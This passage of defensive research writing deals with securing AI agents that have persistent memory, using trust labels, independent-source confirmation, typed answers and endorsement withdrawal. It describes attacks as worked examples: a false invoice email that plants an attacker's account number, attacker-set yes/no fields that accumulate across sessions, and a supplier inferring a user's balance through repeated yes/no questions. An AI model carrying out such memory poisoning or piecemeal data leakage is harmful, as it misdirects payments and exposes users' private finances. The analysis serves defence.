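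Asking users for approval less often is not enough by itself. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise a simulated agent that sometimes went beyond its task. One group set standing rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data, and saw 10.9 prompts on average. Another group had to approve or reject each of the 18 actions. The group with standing rules blocked 20 percentage points less of the unwanted behaviour. They had set 114 of their 140 rules to "ask", and then approved most of what the agent asked about. They had approved 133 of the 148 unwanted actions that went through.

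The content of the prompt seems to matter more. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) asked 80 people to approve or reject an agent's requests, half of which were unsafe. In one scenario, the user allows the agent to send only summary totals to an auditor, but the agent builds the attached file from raw invoice rows. The recipient and file name look fine, and only the file's history shows the problem. Each participant saw one of four kinds of prompt.

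| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact tool call | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The call, the user's original instruction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, arranged to show the overall consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

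The gap between the last two rows could be due to chance, but the drop from 55.0% to 24.2% is large. Each person made only 12 decisions, so the study does not show whether the better prompts would keep working after months of use.

Memory labels can show the user where a remembered value came from. The prompt "Pay 500 euros to the account ending 4471?" gives the user nothing to check the number against. The software could add, "This number came from an email on Monday. You typed a different number for Acme in March." It can produce both sentences from stored labels without calling a model. If the agent asked only when a new account first appeared, rather than at every payment, the user would also have fewer prompts to click through.

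Even a careful user who can confirm that they want to pay Acme may not know whether the account belongs to Acme, and would have to check somewhere else to confirm it.

### Agreement between independent sources

Software can do some of that checking. Under TMA-NM's rule, an untrusted value becomes usable when two independent trusted sources, such as a company's supplier registry and its bank, confirm it. Unlike a user's approval of one action, this confirmation raises the memory's label.

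The weak point of requiring independent confirmation is establishing that the sources are independent. Louck's software, TMA-NM, records which administrative domain each source belongs to and rejects confirmations from the same domain. When an attacker controlled two sources that shared a domain, 67% of attacks succeeded against software that simply counted confirmations, and none succeeded against TMA-NM. But in practice the developer or the company running the agent would have to enter the domains, and the software can't discover a connection that they missed.

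Software cannot always detect that two sources are connected. Suppose a clerk received Acme's false invoice last week and typed its account number into the supplier registry. The bank then checks the number against the payee list that the company uploaded from the same registry. The registry and the bank have different owners and different cryptographic identities, but both got the number from the attacker's email. Louck's definition excludes sources with shared upstream data, so it would rule out this pair, but nothing in the software would reveal that the clerk copied the number. Louck suggests mapping the dependencies between sources and having outside parties attest to their independence.

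Requiring more sources helps protect against compromised ones. In Louck's tests, attackers who controlled two independent sources could defeat a two-source rule but never a three-source rule. Louck recommends two sources for routine, reversible actions, at least three for large payments or changes to permissions, and a new approval from the user for the most serious actions. However, many ordinary facts have only one trusted source, or none. When there are too few sources, TMA-NM asks the user, who may again approve out of habit. Louck has not measured how often this would happen in real use.

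### Narrow answers from untrusted text

A system can also trust an answer that is too small to carry much of an attack. FIDES does this through typed extraction, which limits the quarantined model to a yes or no, or a choice from a fixed list. Constrained decoding enforces the limit by blocking any token that would not fit the format as the model writes. FIDES then adds the answer's type to its label, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no for a consequential action while rejecting untrusted free text. Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their AgentDojo tests, so their results do not show how well it works.

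The quarantined model should not extract the account number from Acme's invoice, because a 20-digit number is far from a narrow answer. It could instead choose which of the user's eight confirmed payees sent the invoice. At worst, an attacker could use that answer to direct a payment to another payee the user already trusts.

The size of an answer limits what an attacker can express, but not how much harm the answer can do. For example, the question "Should the agent skip confirmation from now on?" has a one-bit answer. A developer therefore has to consider what each possible answer would cause, as well as how many there are.

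#### Counting across sessions

Costa and colleagues analyse one answer at a time, within one run. Persistent memory lets answers accumulate. If an agent saves $N$ answers and answer $i$ has $n_i$ options, together they can carry up to

$$C = \sum_{i=1}^{N} \log_2 n_i$$

bits. Ten yes-or-no fields saved in each of thirty sessions can carry 300 bits. A 20-digit account number needs 67, and even the longest international account number, with 34 letters and digits, needs at most 176. An attacker who sends an email before each session could set every field.

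FIDES's labels would not show this growth. FIDES combines labels by taking the larger of the two types, so two yes-or-no answers together are still labelled as a yes or no. After thirty sessions, the planner's context could contain 300 of these answers and have the same label as a context with one.

However, the answers can only become an account number if something inside the agent decodes them. A planner that reads 300 answers to questions like "Is this invoice overdue?" has no reason to turn them into digits, and the attacker can't easily instruct it to. A more plausible danger is that the answers gradually change the planner's judgement. After thirty sessions of "Did Acme deliver on time? Yes", all based on Acme's own emails, the planner might decide that Acme needs less checking.

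Leaks of private data are a greater concern, because an attacker can do the decoding outside the agent. Suppose a policy lets the agent answer a supplier's yes-or-no questions about the user's finances, on the grounds that one bit reveals little. The supplier can find any balance up to a million euros, to the nearest cent, in 27 questions by first asking whether it is above 500,000 euros and then halving the range each time. At one question a week, that takes about six months, and no single session looks suspicious.

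Limits on narrow answers must therefore count across sessions, at least for answers that leave the agent. The software would keep a running total of bits sent to each outside party, store it with the agent's memory, and refuse or ask the user once the total reached a limit. An attacker could get around this by writing from many addresses, so unknown senders should share one total. Ordinary business would also count toward the limit. With a limit of 20 bits, a supplier whose monthly invoice needs five yes-or-no answers would reach it in four months.

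Limiting what the memory holds at one time may be enough for answers that stay inside the agent. If each session overwrites the same ten fields, the memory never holds more than ten of these bits, however many sessions pass. This fails if the agent also keeps a history of the fields or writes notes based on them. Xu and colleagues acknowledge a similar gap in their memory firewall, which checks each action separately and does not fully cover a series of low-risk steps that together cause serious harm.

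### Scope, expiry and withdrawal

An endorsement should apply only to specific uses. Confirming that an account belongs to Acme can justify a payment to Acme, but not a refund to someone else or a change to the user's own bank details. Xu and colleagues' design ties each confirmation to a user, a target and a type of risk.

Endorsements accumulate unless something limits them. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) observes that clicks on "always allow" only enlarge the set of trusted actions. The set of trusted memories also only grows if nothing lowers a label once it is raised. TMA-NM's published design, for example, describes no way to lower a memory's authority after confirmations have raised it.

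An expiry date is the simplest limit. It suits facts that change on a schedule, such as an annual contract price, but a bank account can change the day after the user confirms it. The software could instead end the endorsement when something relevant happens, as EffectMatch does when a supplier is blocked. However, if any email that mentions a new account number cancelled the endorsement, an attacker could make the agent ask for confirmation as often as they liked, and the user might eventually approve the wrong number out of habit. An untrusted email should only add a warning to the next prompt.

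#### When the user withdraws an endorsement

Suppose the user confirms the false account number on Tuesday. Three weeks later, Acme complains that it hasn't received the money, and the user withdraws the confirmation. By then the agent has mentioned the account in a monthly summary, added it to a profile of the user's suppliers and scheduled next month's payment.

If the software changed the number's label to "trusted" on Tuesday and threw away the old one, the summary and the profile would have inherited a trusted label, and nothing would connect them to the confirmation. It is better to leave the original label in place and store the endorsement as a separate record. The software can then work out each memory's label when the agent retrieves it. For a memory $m$ that the agent derived from a set of earlier items $P_m$,

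$$\ell(m) = \begin{cases} \text{the endorsed label} & \text{if } m \text{ has a valid endorsement of its own,} \\ \bigsqcup_{p \in P_m} \ell(p) & \text{otherwise.} \end{cases}$$

While the confirmation is valid, the account number counts as trusted, and so does a summary based on it and other trusted data. When the user withdraws the confirmation, the number regains its original untrusted label, and the summary and the profile become untrusted the next time the agent retrieves them. The counters that Hu and colleagues proposed for ClawMMU could do this efficiently if the software gave each endorsement its own counter.

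If the user also confirmed the supplier profile, the formula leaves the profile labeled trusted, even though the user may have confirmed it only because the account number in it already looked trusted. The software should therefore suspend any later endorsement of a memory derived from the withdrawn one and ask the user again.

Endorsements based on agreement between sources need similar records, so that if a supplier registry turns out to be compromised, the software can find the values the registry helped to confirm. Under a two-source rule, such a value can stay trusted only if two other independent sources also confirmed it.

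Withdrawing an endorsement must also stop actions that depend on it and have not yet happened. EffectMatch saves its decisions for programs that start later to read, and it blocks work that depends on a rejected result. A scheduler that checked endorsements in the same way would cancel next month's payment to the false account. It could not recover the payment already made or correct a summary that the agent had emailed to the user's accountant.

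The effect of withdrawing an endorsement depends on how widely the agent used the endorsed item. If the user had endorsed the whole invoice and let the planner read it, withdrawal would remove the trusted label from every note the planner wrote with the invoice in its context. In Ameur and colleagues' deletion experiments, removing a small share of conversation turns erased most session summaries, which suggests how far the loss of trust could spread. An account number that the planner uses only by name never enters its context, so withdrawing the number's endorsement affects only the entries and scheduled actions that use it.
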